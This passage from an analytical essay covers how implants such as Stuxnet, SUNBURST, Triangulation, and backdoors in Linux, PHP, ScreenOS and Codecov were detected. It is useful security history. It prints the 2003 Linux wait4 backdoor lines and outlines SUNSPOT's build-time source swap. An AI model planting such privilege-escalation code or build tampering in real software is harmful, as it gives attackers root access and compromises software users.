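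The inspectors had no right to ask why, because their job was to account for nuclear material and Iran did not have to explain equipment failures. Zetter writes that the plant's own technicians were apparently just as puzzled. Centrifuges of this type broke often, so the technicians could explain each failure as routine even when the total was far above normal. The Institute for Science and International Security's *Did Stuxnet Take Out 1,000 Centrifuges at the Natanz Enrichment Plant?* dates a major problem with at least 11 groups of centrifuges in one part of the plant to between November 2009 and late January 2010.

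The broken centrifuges were a large-scale runtime anomaly months before the blue screens, yet they did not lead anyone to the implant. The inspectors could count centrifuges but could not examine the controllers. Although Ulasen's anomaly was much smaller, he could connect to the affected computer.

### Working out the purpose

VirusBlokAda had found a worm but did not know what it was for. A few days after Ulasen's forum post, the researcher Frank Boldewin replied with text he had extracted from the decrypted code. The text referred to Siemens's WinCC, and Boldewin guessed that the worm's purpose was espionage. Most antivirus companies added Stuxnet to their scanners and did not investigate further.

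Symantec kept studying Stuxnet, partly because Liam O Murchu, who reviewed major threats there, found the code suspiciously large and dense. It was about 500 kilobytes, while malicious files were usually 10 to 15. Symantec also arranged for infected computers to report to its own server instead of the attackers'. Within a week, about 38,000 computers had reported, about 22,000 of them in Iran, which rarely featured in worldwide outbreaks. On August 6, Symantec reported that Stuxnet could place hidden code on industrial controllers.

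Stuxnet's code showed what its target was. Falliere and colleagues found that it checked for at least 33 frequency converters, devices that set the speed of a motor, from two manufacturers, one in Tehran. A second, disabled attack routine was written for six groups of 164 devices, each arranged in 15 clusters. The centrifuges at Natanz stood in groups of 164, divided into 15 stages. Langner considers this routine by far the best evidence of the target and thinks that leaving it in was a lapse by the attackers.

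Langner's team ran Stuxnet in a laboratory with Siemens equipment. According to The Langner Group's *Stuxnet analysis by Langner*, the team announced on September 16, 2010, that the target was Iran's nuclear program, but few people believed this at first. In November the team published its finding about the prerecorded sensor readings. The Langner Group's *Matching Langner's Stuxnet analysis and Symantec's dossier update* (2011) notes that Symantec confirmed the finding the following February.

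Reverse engineering showed in detail what the attackers wanted to do to the centrifuges. It is less certain whether Stuxnet broke the ones inspectors saw being removed from the plant. The timing fits, but Langner points out that nobody outside Iran knows how many controllers were infected, and that the failures could in theory have had a different cause.

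## How did a newly registered phone lead to the SolarWinds implant?

SolarWinds sells Orion, a program for monitoring and managing computer networks. In 2020, intruders planted a backdoor in Orion's official updates, and up to 18,000 customers downloaded it. MITRE's *SolarWinds Compromise* records that the US and British governments later blamed Russia's foreign intelligence service for the attack. The security company FireEye, an Orion customer, found the backdoor in December 2020 and named it SUNBURST.

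The xz backdoor was noticed because of the processor time it used, and one of Stuxnet's drivers may well have caused the crashes that led Ulasen to the malware. At FireEye, the first signal was a phone the intruders registered once they were inside the network, rather than any effect of the implant's code.

### The second phone

To log in to FireEye's network, employees needed their usual credentials and a code sent to a registered phone. In late November 2020, an alert showed that a second phone had been registered to one employee's account. In *Prepared Statement of Kevin Mandia, CEO of FireEye, Inc*, Mandia (2021) told the US House of Representatives that such registrations are common when a popular new phone comes out. He said FireEye's staff followed up the alert anyway and established that the employee had not registered a new device.

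That left few innocent explanations. An intruder with a stolen password still needs the code, and registering another phone is a simple way to receive it.

Few companies could have investigated as thoroughly as FireEye, whose business is responding to break-ins at other companies. It put about 100 people on the case. Mandia told a Senate hearing, three days before his House testimony, that FireEye had asked Microsoft and US intelligence agencies about the internet addresses used in the attack (Senate Select Committee on Intelligence, *Open Hearing*, 2022). Nobody had seen them before, so a list of known hostile addresses would not have helped.

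On December 8, FireEye announced that intruders had stolen tools it used to test its customers' defenses. It still did not know how they had broken in. Many victims would have changed every password, rebuilt the affected machines and stopped investigating, leaving the implant in place.

### Taking Orion apart

FireEye's investigators examined thousands of computers for the earliest trace of the intruders. Mandia told NPR that the trail ended at a server running SolarWinds software. But the investigators could find nothing malicious on that server.

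FireEye's technical report on the backdoor, *Highly Evasive Attacker Leverages SolarWinds Supply Chain to Compromise Multiple Global Victims*, suggests why. The intruders routinely removed their tools and preferred to use legitimate credentials once they had them. SUNBURST was hidden in an ordinary Orion component that had a valid SolarWinds digital signature. It waited up to two weeks and checked for security software before contacting anyone, and its network traffic imitated that of a genuine Orion feature.

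A server with an early trace of the intrusion and no visible malware could easily have been a dead end, because the intruders might have reached it from another machine and then deleted the evidence on that machine. Mandia told the Senate that the Orion software was "the last place you'd look", and the investigators turned to it only after they had run out of other leads.

FireEye then reverse engineered the whole product. The update contained over 18,000 files. According to the NPR interview, more than 4,000 of these were executable, and FireEye decompiled them, turning them back into millions of lines of something resembling source code. Mandia gave the Senate somewhat lower figures of 3,500 executable files and over a million lines of assembly, the readable form of machine instructions. Both figures are far more code than anyone would read on a hunch.

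Finding the right file was most of the difficulty. The component that held SUNBURST was written for .NET, a Microsoft platform whose compiled files keep much of the information in the source. CrowdStrike's *SUNSPOT*, an analysis by a security company SolarWinds hired, shows part of the backdoor's source beside a decompiled version, and the two are almost the same. An analyst who opened the compiled file and knew what to look for could read the implant much as a source reviewer would.

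FireEye told SolarWinds about the implant on December 12, four days after announcing its own breach, and published its findings the next day. The doctored component it described had been signed on March 24, so the dwell time was at least 263 days.

Reverse engineering also helped customers who had noticed nothing. FireEye found that SUNBURST would permanently shut itself down under a certain condition, and worked with Microsoft and the internet company GoDaddy to create that condition. This disabled the backdoor even on machines that no investigator had examined, but it couldn't remove intruders who already had another way to stay in a network.

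The intruders triggered the alert by using stolen employee credentials, so the alert did not detect SUNBURST itself. Mandia told the Senate that they came in through the implant and immediately took credentials so they could log in as employees did. If they had left the employee's account alone, the implant would still have been on FireEye's server, but FireEye would have had no reason to look for it.

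Most customers were in that position. NPR's *A 'worst nightmare' cyberattack* explains that the hack worked only if a customer installed the update on a network connected to the internet. Even then, the intruders usually did nothing more. The government knew of about 100 organizations where they had gone further, and according to the Senate hearing, some victims did not use SolarWinds software at all. So at more than 99% of the customers who downloaded the backdoor, there was probably no later activity to notice.

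### A source file that changed only during the build

The intruders did not add SUNBURST to the source code that SolarWinds stored. They got into a server that built Orion and installed a tool there, which CrowdStrike calls SUNSPOT. It worked as follows:

1. A scheduled task started SUNSPOT whenever the server booted. Every second, SUNSPOT searched the list of running programs for MsBuild.exe, a Microsoft program that manages builds.
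2. When it found one, it read the command that had started the program from the program's memory, to see whether the build was for Orion.
3. If so, it calculated a checksum of one source file, InventoryManager.cs, and compared it with the value the intruders expected. If they matched, SUNSPOT saved a copy of the file and put a version containing SUNBURST in its place.
4. The compiler read the altered file like any other. When the build program finished, SUNSPOT restored the original file and deleted the saved copy.

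SolarWinds then signed the finished component itself, so the signature was genuine. The malicious version of InventoryManager.cs existed only while the build was running, so a reviewer who read every line of Orion's stored source would have found nothing wrong. In the xz attack, by contrast, the altered build file was in the public release archives, where a determined reader could have found it.

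The intruders worked hard to avoid failed builds, which developers would have investigated. The checksum in the third step kept SUNSPOT from replacing the file if SolarWinds's developers had changed it, since an outdated replacement might not have compiled. The added code included instructions that switched off compiler warnings for the malicious lines. The intruders also had a way to make SUNSPOT finish its current work and exit, because killing it mid-swap could have left altered source on the server.

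The intruders also rehearsed the attack. Mandia said that they added harmless code to an Orion build in October 2019 to see whether it would reach customers, and it did. They inserted the real backdoor months later. They seem to have worked out in advance which anomalies the developers would notice, unlike the xz attackers, who never fixed their implant's excessive processor use.

If Orion's builds had been reproducible, SolarWinds could have caught the swap by building the program again on a separate, clean machine and comparing the results. Customers could not have run this check because they did not have the source code.

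Investigators first found SUNSPOT when they examined the build server after FireEye's disclosure. CrowdStrike's rules for detecting it date from January 8, 2021, about six weeks after the alert about the phone.

### The warnings before December

The US Justice Department had noticed something wrong six months before FireEye did. In *SolarWinds Detected Six Months Earlier* (2023), the security writer Bruce Schneier quotes an investigation by the magazine Wired. Wired's sources say that in late May 2020 the department saw unusual traffic from a server running a trial version of Orion, which was communicating with an unfamiliar system on the internet. The department asked the security firm Mandiant whether someone had hacked the server, and it also brought in Microsoft.

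The investigators suspected that hackers had broken into the server directly, perhaps through a flaw in Orion. They contacted SolarWinds, whose engineers could not find a vulnerability in their code. Communication stopped in July with the traffic still unexplained, and in August the department bought Orion.

FireEye owned Mandiant, so the company that found SUNBURST in December had been consulted months earlier about a server running it. The department's signal was also better, because the traffic came from the Orion server itself. FireEye's alert concerned an employee's phone and led to Orion only after weeks of forensic work.

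The engineers probably looked for the wrong thing because they suspected an ordinary flaw. A vulnerability is a mistake that an outsider could exploit, whereas SUNBURST was a working feature that someone had added on purpose. If they searched the stored source, they could not have found it anyway. Fedora's developers similarly treated the xz errors as a bug.

The public did not hear the full story for almost three years. Techzine's *Department of Justice already knew of SolarWinds hack in May 2020* notes that the department previously said it learned of the hack on December 24, 2020.

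The US financial regulator SEC (2023) gives a second account in its complaint against SolarWinds and its security chief, Brown. According to the complaint, an unnamed government agency installed Orion in May 2020 and then reported that it was contacting unknown websites. Insurance Journal (2023) notes that Wired had identified this agency as the Justice Department. The complaint alleges that SolarWinds's investigation found "numerous" vulnerabilities, some of them years old, but not the cause of the traffic. This fits Wired's account if none of those vulnerabilities explained the traffic. Finding so many real flaws may even have made the wrong explanation more believable.

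According to the complaint, Brown thought an attacker was either already in the agency's system or studying Orion to use it in larger attacks. The second possibility was close to the truth, but the attackers had finished studying Orion and were already using it.

In October 2020, an unnamed cybersecurity company also reported malicious activity by Orion. The complaint alleges that SolarWinds employees recognized the resemblance to the agency's case, but told this customer they had not seen such behavior before. The employee who said so messaged a colleague during the call to admit it was a lie. SolarWinds staff blamed a patch that the customer had not installed. The customer replied that the cause looked like an unknown vulnerability, and urged SolarWinds to treat the incident as the work of an outside attacker.

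These are allegations from an SEC complaint, and a court dismissed most of the claims in it (Harvard Law School Forum on Corporate Governance, *Court Dismisses Most of SEC’s Claims Against SolarWinds*, 2024). Those claims, however, were about whether SolarWinds had misled investors. The complaint is also not the only evidence of earlier warnings. SC Media reported that SolarWinds itself had acknowledged two customer inquiries that looked related in hindsight.

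According to the complaint, a customer that can only be FireEye showed Brown the decompiled code on December 12. By the next day at the latest, Brown had connected it with both earlier incidents, and he later testified that this had required no further analysis. The code explained two anomalies that SolarWinds had been unable to explain for months.

The security company Volexity also came close to finding the implant. Its *Dark Halo Leverages SolarWinds Compromise to Breach Organizations* (2020), published the day after FireEye's report, connected SUNBURST with several incidents that Volexity had already worked on. According to a passage that a reader quoted in the comments on Schneier's post, Volexity had concluded that the infection probably came from a SolarWinds server but could not tell how the intruders had got in. An unknown flaw was one possibility. Several restarts had already wiped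 evidence from the machines' memory. Volexity therefore felt unable to report the circumstances to SolarWinds.

Like FireEye, Volexity suspected an Orion server but had no evidence of what was wrong with it. FireEye then took the Orion software apart, which Mandia told NPR most companies cannot do.

According to the US cybersecurity agency CISA, Volexity found that the intruders in one of its cases had stolen a secret key and used it to forge a browser cookie, a small file that showed the email system they had already passed the second login check. An intruder who can do this doesn't need to register a phone, so an alert like FireEye's would not have gone off.

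At the Senate hearing, the committee's chairman, Mark Warner, wondered whether the breach would still be unknown if FireEye had not detected it and come forward. His worry was reasonable, because several capable organizations had earlier suspected an Orion server and none had found the implant. But reports were accumulating, and by October at least one customer was pressing SolarWinds hard. Someone might well have found SUNBURST without the phone, though probably not in December.

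### How many innocent phones for each hostile one?

It is easy in hindsight to say that everyone should investigate odd events the way FireEye did. A rough calculation shows why they can't. Take a company with 3,300 employees, about the size of FireEye. All the other numbers here are invented:

- Each employee registers a new phone once every three years. This makes 1,100 innocent registrations a year, or 11,000 in ten years.
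- An intruder registers a phone once in those ten years.
- The alert system always flags the intruder's phone. It also flags 10% of the innocent ones, for example because the old phone is still registered.
- When asked about an innocent registration, one employee in 100 wrongly denies it, perhaps having forgotten about a tablet.

| Registrations over ten years | Innocent ones for each hostile one | Next check |
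|---|---|---|
| All registrations | 11,000 | The automatic alert |
| Those that the system flags | 1,100 | A five-minute conversation with the employee |
| Those that the employee denies | 11 | A day spent reading login records |

The system flags only 10% of innocent registrations, but 1,100 of its 1,101 alerts are false because hostile registrations are so rare. If there are *n* innocent registrations and *h* hostile ones, and the system flags a share *f* of the innocent and *d* of the hostile, the chance that an alert is real is *dh* / (*dh* + *fn*). With the numbers above, that is 1 / (1 + 1,100), or about 0.09%. After a denial, the chance rises to one in 12, or about 8%.

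The conversations would take about 92 hours over the ten years, and the 12 days of reading login records would take another 96. That is less than five weeks of one person's work in a decade, which is little time to spend on catching an intruder.

The work would not seem worthwhile to the person doing it, who would have about nine conversations a month and would almost certainly change jobs before one of them mattered. That person would be most tempted to skip the conversation just after a popular phone went on sale. If a quarter of the year's new phones arrived in one month, the system would raise 27 or 28 alerts that month, nearly all because someone had bought a new phone.

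The result depends heavily on how often intruders register phones, and no company knows its own rate. If an intruder registers a phone once a century instead of once a decade, there are 110 innocent denials for each hostile one. A better alert system helps only in proportion, so halving the share of innocent phones it flags halves the number of conversations.

FireEye could easily learn a lot about its alert by asking the employee whether the phone was theirs. The Justice Department could ask only SolarWinds about the traffic from its Orion server, and SolarWinds' engineers couldn't explain it either. The next available check was to take apart thousands of files in a reputable supplier's product, at a time when an ordinary break-in seemed a much likelier explanation.

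## How did network traffic reveal spyware on iPhones that could not be inspected?

In early 2023, the Moscow-based security company Kaspersky noticed suspicious traffic from its employees' iPhones. An iPhone is harder to investigate than the Orion server whose traffic had puzzled the US Justice Department, because Apple gives outsiders no standard way to see what is running on it. Kaspersky still traced the traffic to spyware, and on June 1, 2023, it disclosed the attack, which it called Operation Triangulation.

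The attackers sent each victim a message with an attachment through iMessage, Apple's messaging service. The phone processed the attachment without showing a notification. A series of exploits, code that takes advantage of flaws, then took control of the phone and loaded the spyware without the owner tapping anything. In *A matter of triangulation* (2023), the company's head, Eugene Kaspersky, wrote that the attack had infected several dozen iPhones belonging to senior employees. The spyware sent out microphone recordings, photos from messaging apps and the phone's location.

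### A pattern in unreadable traffic

Kaspersky had a separate Wi-Fi network for mobile devices and monitored its traffic. In *How to catch a wild triangle*, Kaspersky describes the sequence that investigators found when they recorded the connections:

1. A phone contacted the iMessage servers and downloaded a small amount of data that could have been an attachment.
2. It exchanged data with a server named backuprabbit for less than a minute.
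3. It held a longer session with one of five other servers, which had names such as unlimitedteacup and virtuallaughing.
4. When the phone restarted, the suspicious connections stopped.

The order of events suggested that something was reaching the phones through iMessage. It probably existed only in the phones' working memory, because the connections stopped after a restart. The phones used HTTPS, the standard encryption for web traffic, so the investigators could see when a phone contacted a server and how much data it exchanged, but not what the data was. The traffic was a good reason to investigate, especially as several phones showed the same pattern. But the investigators could not use it to identify the program responsible or prove malice, because many harmless apps also send usage statistics to servers with odd names.

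Kaspersky sells the monitoring system it credits with the detection, but its evidence does not depend on that product. Any complete record of the connections would have shown the same sequence.

### Matching the traffic to a backup

The investigators had the infected phones in the office and wanted to copy their entire storage. Forensic tools made such copies by exploiting flaws in a phone's protections, as the attackers had done, but the tools available at the time did not work on phones with modern processors running iOS 15 or 16. Even a full copy would not have contained the spyware, because it ran only in memory.

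The investigators turned to iTunes backups, which contain some of a phone's files and databases. They assumed the attackers were listening through the phones' microphones and reading email, so they worked in secret and met in person, with the phones in airplane mode and sometimes in bags that block radio signals. They later found that the spyware did have a module for recording sound.

The investigators used a free program, the Mobile Verification Toolkit, to arrange the timestamps in each backup into a timeline. They first searched the iMessage folders, where the research group Citizen Lab had found another spyware exploit in 2021. They found no exploit there and no malicious program anywhere in the backups. Someone with only the backups might reasonably have concluded that the phones were clean.

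But the investigators also had the Wi-Fi records, which showed when each phone had made the suspicious connections. They looked for events that recurred in the timeline at those times and found that a process named BackupAgent had been using the network. Apple had retired this program years earlier, so it should not have run at all. In its first public report, Kaspersky (2023) called these records the most reliable sign of infection and printed an example from September 13, 2022:

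| Time | What the backup recorded |
|---|---|
| 10:04:11 | The process that downloads iMessage attachments used the network |
| 10:04:54 | An attachment folder changed, although it contained no file |
| 10:05:14 | BackupAgent had received about 734,000 bytes and sent about 288,000 |

When a folder has just changed but is empty, something has usually deleted a file from it. The timeline therefore showed an attachment arriving and disappearing, followed within seconds by network activity from a program that should not have been running. This was strong evidence of a compromise, but it did not show how the attackers had got in, what code was running under BackupAgent's name or what that code had sent.

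The attackers had tried to remove such evidence. According to Kaspersky's *The outstanding stealth of Operation Triangulation*, one component deleted crash logs and searched several databases for traces of the malicious message. Once the spyware was running, its operators copied more logs to their server and deleted them from the phone. They could also set the microphone module to stop recording whenever the screen came on. Software with this much control could presumably have deleted BackupAgent's network records too, so the investigators were probably lucky that the attackers overlooked them.

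### Checking other phones

The investigators wrote a program, triangle_check, that searches a backup for the BackupAgent record. It let them check colleagues' phones quickly, and the company released it to the public the day after the disclosure. Kaspersky's *In search of the Triangulation* explains its three possible results. "Detected" means the program found a specific sign of infection, and "suspicion" means it found a combination of weaker signs. The third result, that it found no traces, is less informative because an attacker who deleted the right records would produce the same result, and publishing the program showed attackers which records to delete.

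Owners could also see one anomaly, because the spyware changed a settings file so that iOS updates failed with an error message. But the message described a download problem, which few people would attribute to spyware.

### Capturing the code

With no exploit or spyware in the backups, the investigators had to catch the code the next time it arrived. They could count on another attempt because the spyware did not survive a restart, which Kaspersky attributes to the limitations of iOS. Eugene Kaspersky blamed Apple's closed design for the whole incident, calling iOS a "black box" where spyware can hide for years. The closed design had indeed stopped his staff from copying the phones. But the same restrictions probably helped them too, because each reinfection sent more traffic across the Wi-Fi network and gave them another chance to capture the code.

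The first attempt failed. The investigators logged in to a spare Mac with the accounts of several targeted colleagues and ran a script to record incoming iMessages. The network monitor soon showed that the attackers had infected a phone that shared one of these accounts, but the Mac had recorded no message at that time, and Kaspersky never found out why. Without the network monitor, the investigators could have concluded from the empty record that no attack had happened.

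They then routed traffic from previously infected phones through their own server. They installed a certificate that made the phones trust this server, so it could decrypt HTTPS traffic and pass it on. This worked for traffic to the attackers' servers but not for iMessage, because iOS accepts only particular certificates for most Apple services. At the next infection, the investigators captured a validator, a script that gathers details about a phone so that the attackers can avoid sending their exploits to a security researcher's test device.

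The validator and the later stages added their own encryption, using keys that an eavesdropper could not recover from the traffic. The investigators' server therefore altered the attackers' code on its way to the phone:

| What the investigators wanted to read | What their server changed |
|---|---|
| The validator's messages | It replaced the random encryption key with one the investigators had chosen |
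| The spyware | It removed the step that encrypted the phone's request for the spyware, then encrypted the request itself with a known key |
| The spyware's extra modules | It replaced the attackers' public key with the investigators' own, then re-encrypted each message for the attackers |

One captured component contained a command for erasing traces of the malicious message. The command searched for watch-face files, so the investigators knew what kind of attachment to look for. iMessage encrypts an attachment, stores it on Apple's iCloud servers and sends the key to the phone separately. The investigators could intercept the encrypted file but not the key. They changed a few bytes of the file in transit, which made the download fail. Because the exploit never ran, it could not delete the key from the phone's message database. The investigators then recovered the key from a backup of the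 phone.

Kaspersky took about half a year to collect the whole chain. In *Dissecting TriangleDB*, it describes an implant with 24 commands, including ones for copying files, stealing saved passwords and tracking the phone's location. These commands left no doubt that the implant was malicious. The chain also used four zero-days, which Kaspersky reported to Apple.

One of the four weaknesses depended on a feature of Apple's chips that no one outside the company was known to have documented. Larin, Bezvershenko and Kucherin (2023) searched firmware, kernel files and public source code and found no reference to the addresses the exploit used. Reading the phone's software in advance would probably not have revealed this weakness.

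### The view from outside the phone

An implant that controls a device can falsify what the device reports about itself, as Stuxnet did. But to be useful, spyware has to send data to its operators over a network that someone else can monitor. Encryption hides the content, but the network's owner can still see when the device connects, to which address, and how much data it sends.

Network monitoring can reveal spyware only if the spyware's data crosses the monitored network. In the September 2022 example, BackupAgent's Wi-Fi counters were zero and all its data had gone over the mobile network. Kaspersky's monitor could not have recorded that traffic, and the company learned of it only from the backup. The spyware also had an option to send the contents of files only over Wi-Fi, perhaps to avoid using the victim's mobile data. On a monitored office network, this option would have made the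 largest transfers easier to notice.

Someone also has to recognize the traffic as suspicious. SUNBURST made this difficult by imitating a genuine Orion feature. The Triangulation attackers, by contrast, used servers that employees' phones had no obvious reason to contact, and they infected dozens of phones at one company, so the same sequence kept recurring in the traffic.

The oldest traces dated from 2019, so the campaign went undetected for at least three years, and it was still going on when Kaspersky disclosed it. Investigators can look back this far partly because an iPhone set up from an older phone's data inherits the old records. Some of the spyware's modules included code for versions of iOS that were common before 2015, so parts of the toolkit may be much older than the known infections. The earlier infections may have gone undetected because they used mostly the mobile network,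 or because their traffic crossed the Wi-Fi network without anyone noticing the pattern.

### The same framework in Coruna

Apple fixed the flaws that Kaspersky reported, but the developers kept working on their tools. In March 2026, Google Threat Intelligence Group's *Coruna* (2026) described a kit of 23 iPhone exploits that worked on iOS 13 to 17.2.1. Google had first captured parts of the kit in February 2025, when a customer of a surveillance company was using it. That summer, Google found the same code on hacked Ukrainian websites, where a suspected Russian espionage group had put it. By the end of the year, criminals operating from China were using the full kit on fake financial websites. They had left a debug version on one of these sites, and it revealed the developers' apparent name for the kit, Coruna.

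Two of Coruna's exploits used flaws that the Triangulation attackers had also used. This was weak evidence of a connection, because details of the flaws had long been public and other researchers had written their own exploits for them. Kaspersky's *Coruna* gives much better evidence from the code itself. One of the kit's five kernel exploits is an updated version of Triangulation's, and the other four share code with it.

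The updated exploit checks for iOS 17.2 and for processors released in late 2023, although Apple had already fixed the flaws it relies on in a test version of iOS 16.5. These checks are useless to that exploit but necessary for the newer ones in the kit, so the developers probably built all five exploits from the same source code and recompiled the old one along with the others. They wrote two of the five after Kaspersky exposed Triangulation.

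The company states this conclusion with varying confidence. Its technical analysis says "we assume" that Coruna is an updated version of a framework that Triangulation used at least to some extent. In a press release, Kaspersky (2026) is confident that the same author created the kernel exploits in both. The shared code is good evidence for a common author, but it does not identify who attacked Kaspersky's employees, and Fortune (2023) noted that the company had not named a culprit. Schneier on Security's *Possible US Government iPhone Hacking Tool Leaked* (2026) quotes a TechCrunch report in which two anonymous former employees of the US contractor L3Harris said that its Trenchant division had developed Coruna at least in part. Even if they are right, knowing who built the kit would not show who used the earlier version, because at least three groups used Coruna in 2025 alone.

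Attackers were still using exploits from the Coruna family in November 2026. In *MoldyRoost*, Roshan and Stein (2026) linked more than 480 advertising domains to an operation that spread such exploits in over 47 countries. Opening the page behind one of the ads was enough to infect a vulnerable iPhone. Google found that Coruna does not work against the latest version of iOS, so only people who have not updated their phones are at risk.

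## When has reading or comparing code found an implant?

The investigations of xz, Stuxnet, SolarWinds and Triangulation all began with something odd on a running system or network. Others began when somebody read code or compared two copies of it. The best documented of these investigations involved the Linux kernel in November 2003.

### Two extra lines in a copy of Linux

At that time, Linux's developers kept the main copy of the kernel's source in BitKeeper, a repository system. Some developers preferred not to use it, so BitKeeper's maker, BitMover, published a mirror through an older system, CVS. New code should have reached the mirror only from BitKeeper.

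BitMover's Larry McVoy did not take this for granted. As McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, explained to the kernel developers' mailing list, a scheduled job updated the mirror and checked it every night:

1. It fetched the BitKeeper source to one of BitMover's internal machines.
2. It converted the source to CVS form there.
3. It copied the updated files to the public CVS server.
4. It calculated checksums for the internal and public copies, compared them, and emailed BitMover if they differed.

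On November 5, the comparison flagged a file called exit.c. The conversion always added a reference to a BitKeeper change to each entry in the public history, but three of this file's entries had none. The earliest added two lines and listed the kernel developer David Miller as its author, but Miller denied making the change. McVoy tested whether the conversion program was at fault, then repaired the file and told the list that it was "not a big deal".

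A reader asked, out of curiosity, what the changed lines were. McVoy posted them:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines were in the code for wait4, which a program calls to wait for another program it started. They look like an error check that rejects an odd combination of options. In the code, current->uid is the number of the user running the program, and user 0 is root, the administrator who can do anything on the machine. In C, "== 0" tests whether a value is zero, while "= 0" sets it to zero. The line had only one equals sign, so it made the caller root instead of checking whether the caller was root.

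C evaluates the part after && only if the part before it is true, so the assignment ran only when a program called wait4 with exactly those two options. The assignment counts as false because its value is zero, so the second line, which sets an error code, never ran. The parentheses that C requires around the assignment also kept the compiler from warning about it.

Ten minutes after McVoy posted the lines, one reader said they looked odd. Fifteen minutes later, Chad Kitching wrote that they looked like an attempt to backdoor the kernel, and McVoy replied that he had missed that.

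The checksums had located the change but not revealed its purpose, and McVoy had handled the file for hours without recognizing it. Readers on the list worked it out in less than half an hour, but they were looking at two lines that somebody had already identified as illegitimate. Dilger (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, thought that the same change might have taken "a good while to find" if it had been slipped into the kernel without review.

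Later accounts tend to omit the checksum comparison that, according to McVoy, first flagged the file. The blog Freedom to Tinker, for example, says McVoy noticed a change with no record of approval.

Linus Torvalds, who leads Linux development, told the mailing list that the change could not have reached an official release, because developers who merged code directly used BitKeeper and he would have read any emailed patch to such a central file. McVoy was less confident, because a developer working from the CVS copy could have unknowingly included the two lines in a patch.

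### A "typo" in PHP

Source review was almost entirely responsible for finding the implant in PHP, a programming language that many websites run on. On March 28, 2021, somebody pushed a change to PHP's main repository under the name of the language's creator, Rasmus Lerdorf. According to PHP.Watch's *git.php.net server compromised, move to GitHub, and delayed updates* (2021), the accompanying message was "[skip-ci] Fix typo". Git, the repository system, lets people enter any name as the author.

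The change let an outsider run code on a website by sending a request with a header that began with "zerodium". BleepingComputer reported that Michael Voříšek first questioned the change and that another developer, Jake Birchall, explained what it did. Nikita Popov, a PHP maintainer, said that the team found it within a couple of hours, during routine review of new commits, and that it was "rather obviously malicious". About 12 hours after the first push, the attacker tried again in Popov's name. WeLiveSecurity (2021) notes that this second commit was presented as a revert of the first. The developers removed the backdoor before any official release.

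Reading the code raised the first suspicion of the PHP implant, located it and confirmed it. It helped that the change was small, that its trigger was plain text, much like heron-4471, and that PHP's developers routinely read each other's commits after they entered the repository. A nightly comparison like McVoy's would have found nothing, because PHP's GitHub mirror had copied the malicious commits.

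Automatic testing might have caught the change too. When Kokkonis and colleagues replayed the first commit, their fuzzing tool Lily detected the backdoor in 16 of 20 runs. But "[skip-ci]" is an instruction to skip a project's automatic tests, so it would probably have stopped Lily from running. Kokkonis and colleagues suggest running Lily on the hosting platform, where a project's developers cannot switch it off.

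### A changed number in ScreenOS

In December 2015, Juniper Networks announced that it had found unauthorized code in ScreenOS, the software of its NetScreen firewalls, during "a recent internal code review" (Worrall, 2015, *Important Announcement about ScreenOS*). Of the two changes, one gave an attacker administrative access and the other made it possible to decrypt the traffic of virtual private networks (VPNs), the encrypted connections that companies use between offices.

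This is weaker evidence for source review than it first appears, because Juniper did not explain what prompted the review, which might have been routine or a reaction to something suspicious. Bloomberg's *Juniper Breach Mystery Starts to Clear With New Details on Hackers* (2021), which draws on an internal document and two people involved in the investigation, reports that Juniper had already detected intrusions in 2012 and 2014 but took them for separate attempts to steal trade secrets. In 2012 it learned that the hackers had taken ScreenOS source code from an engineer's computer. It did not notice that they came back soon afterwards and altered the code on a server where it prepared new versions, so the VPN backdoor lasted about three years or more.

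That backdoor would have been hard to recognize by reading the code. ScreenOS generated its encryption keys with an algorithm called Dual EC, which relies on a large fixed number, Q. Whoever chooses Q can work out the keys. The hackers replaced Juniper's Q with their own, and a reviewer cannot tell who chose a long number by looking at it. Comparing the file with an older version would show that Q had changed, and the reviewer could then ask who had authorized the change. The administrative backdoor was a master password disguised as debugging code. Stephen Checkoway and colleagues later reverse engineered ScreenOS to work out what the changes did, in a study that Schneier quotes in *Details about Juniper's Firewall Backdoor*.

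Still, waiting for a runtime anomaly would have been a poor alternative, because an eavesdropper can record encrypted traffic and decrypt it elsewhere without changing how the firewall behaves. Juniper told customers they could not tell whether this had happened to them.

Reading may also have exposed an older backdoor, in Dual EC itself. In 2007, Microsoft researchers published a warning that the algorithm probably contained a backdoor, because the US National Security Agency (NSA), which wrote it, had also recommended the value of Q. Leaked NSA documents later supported their suspicion. Juniper added the algorithm in 2008 despite the warning. Bloomberg's sources say that the company's engineers knew about the warning but that the Pentagon, a major customer, insisted on it being added.

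### One customer who checked a checksum

Codecov, a company that measures how much of a program its tests exercise, distributed a script called the Bash Uploader, which customers' test systems downloaded and ran automatically. CISA's *Codecov Releases New Detections for Supply Chain Compromise* (2021) dates the first unauthorized change to the script to January 31, 2021, and its discovery to April 1, 60 days later.

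The attacker extracted a storage key from a software image that Codecov published, and used it to replace the script on Codecov's download server. The altered version collected environment variables, settings that often include passwords and keys for other services. Codecov's *Post-Mortem / Root Cause Analysis (April 2021)* (2021) reports that one customer calculated the checksum of the downloaded script, saw that it did not match the one Codecov had published on GitHub, and emailed the company.

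The comparison worked because the script and its checksum were in different places. The stolen key let the attacker change files in Codecov's cloud storage but not on GitHub. If Codecov had kept the checksum beside the script, the attacker could have replaced both.

Any customer could have made this check on the first day, though Codecov admitted that it had never properly documented how. Few people seem to have done so, and even some software experts did not. Stinner (2021), in *Code coverage on the CI*, reported that the Python programming language's own test systems had been downloading and running the script without validating it.

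Codecov's mismatch was also much more informative than most mismatches in rebuilt Python packages, which often differ for harmless reasons. Two copies of a short script should be identical. So should the two CVS copies of Linux, although McVoy still had to rule out a fault in the conversion.

### What comparisons would have caught

Two kinds of comparison are available to projects that publish their source. The simpler one checks the published source, such as a release archive, against the repository and lists every file that differs. The other relies on reproducible builds and checks the published binary against an independent rebuild. Each would have worked in some of these cases:

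| Implant | Published source against repository | Independent rebuild against published binary |
|---|---|---|
| xz | Lists the altered build file, among harmless extras | Differs only if the rebuild starts from the repository |
| SolarWinds | Finds nothing, as the stored source was clean | Differs, if the second build machine is clean |
| Linux, 2003 | Differs, as McVoy found | Differs only if the rebuild starts from BitKeeper |
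| PHP | Finds nothing | Finds nothing |
| ScreenOS | Depends on which copies the hackers altered | Depends on which copies the hackers altered |
| Codecov | Differs, as the customer found | Does not apply to a script that nobody compiles |

The xz row shows a limit of reproducible builds. They guarantee that a binary matches its source, but someone must choose which source to build from. If every builder starts from the doctored release archive, they all produce the same backdoored library, with matching checksums. Building from the repository produces a clean library, as Freund found by accident.

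In the SolarWinds case, only the rebuild would have helped. Both comparisons are worth doing, because one covers the step from repository to archive and the other covers the step from archive to binary.

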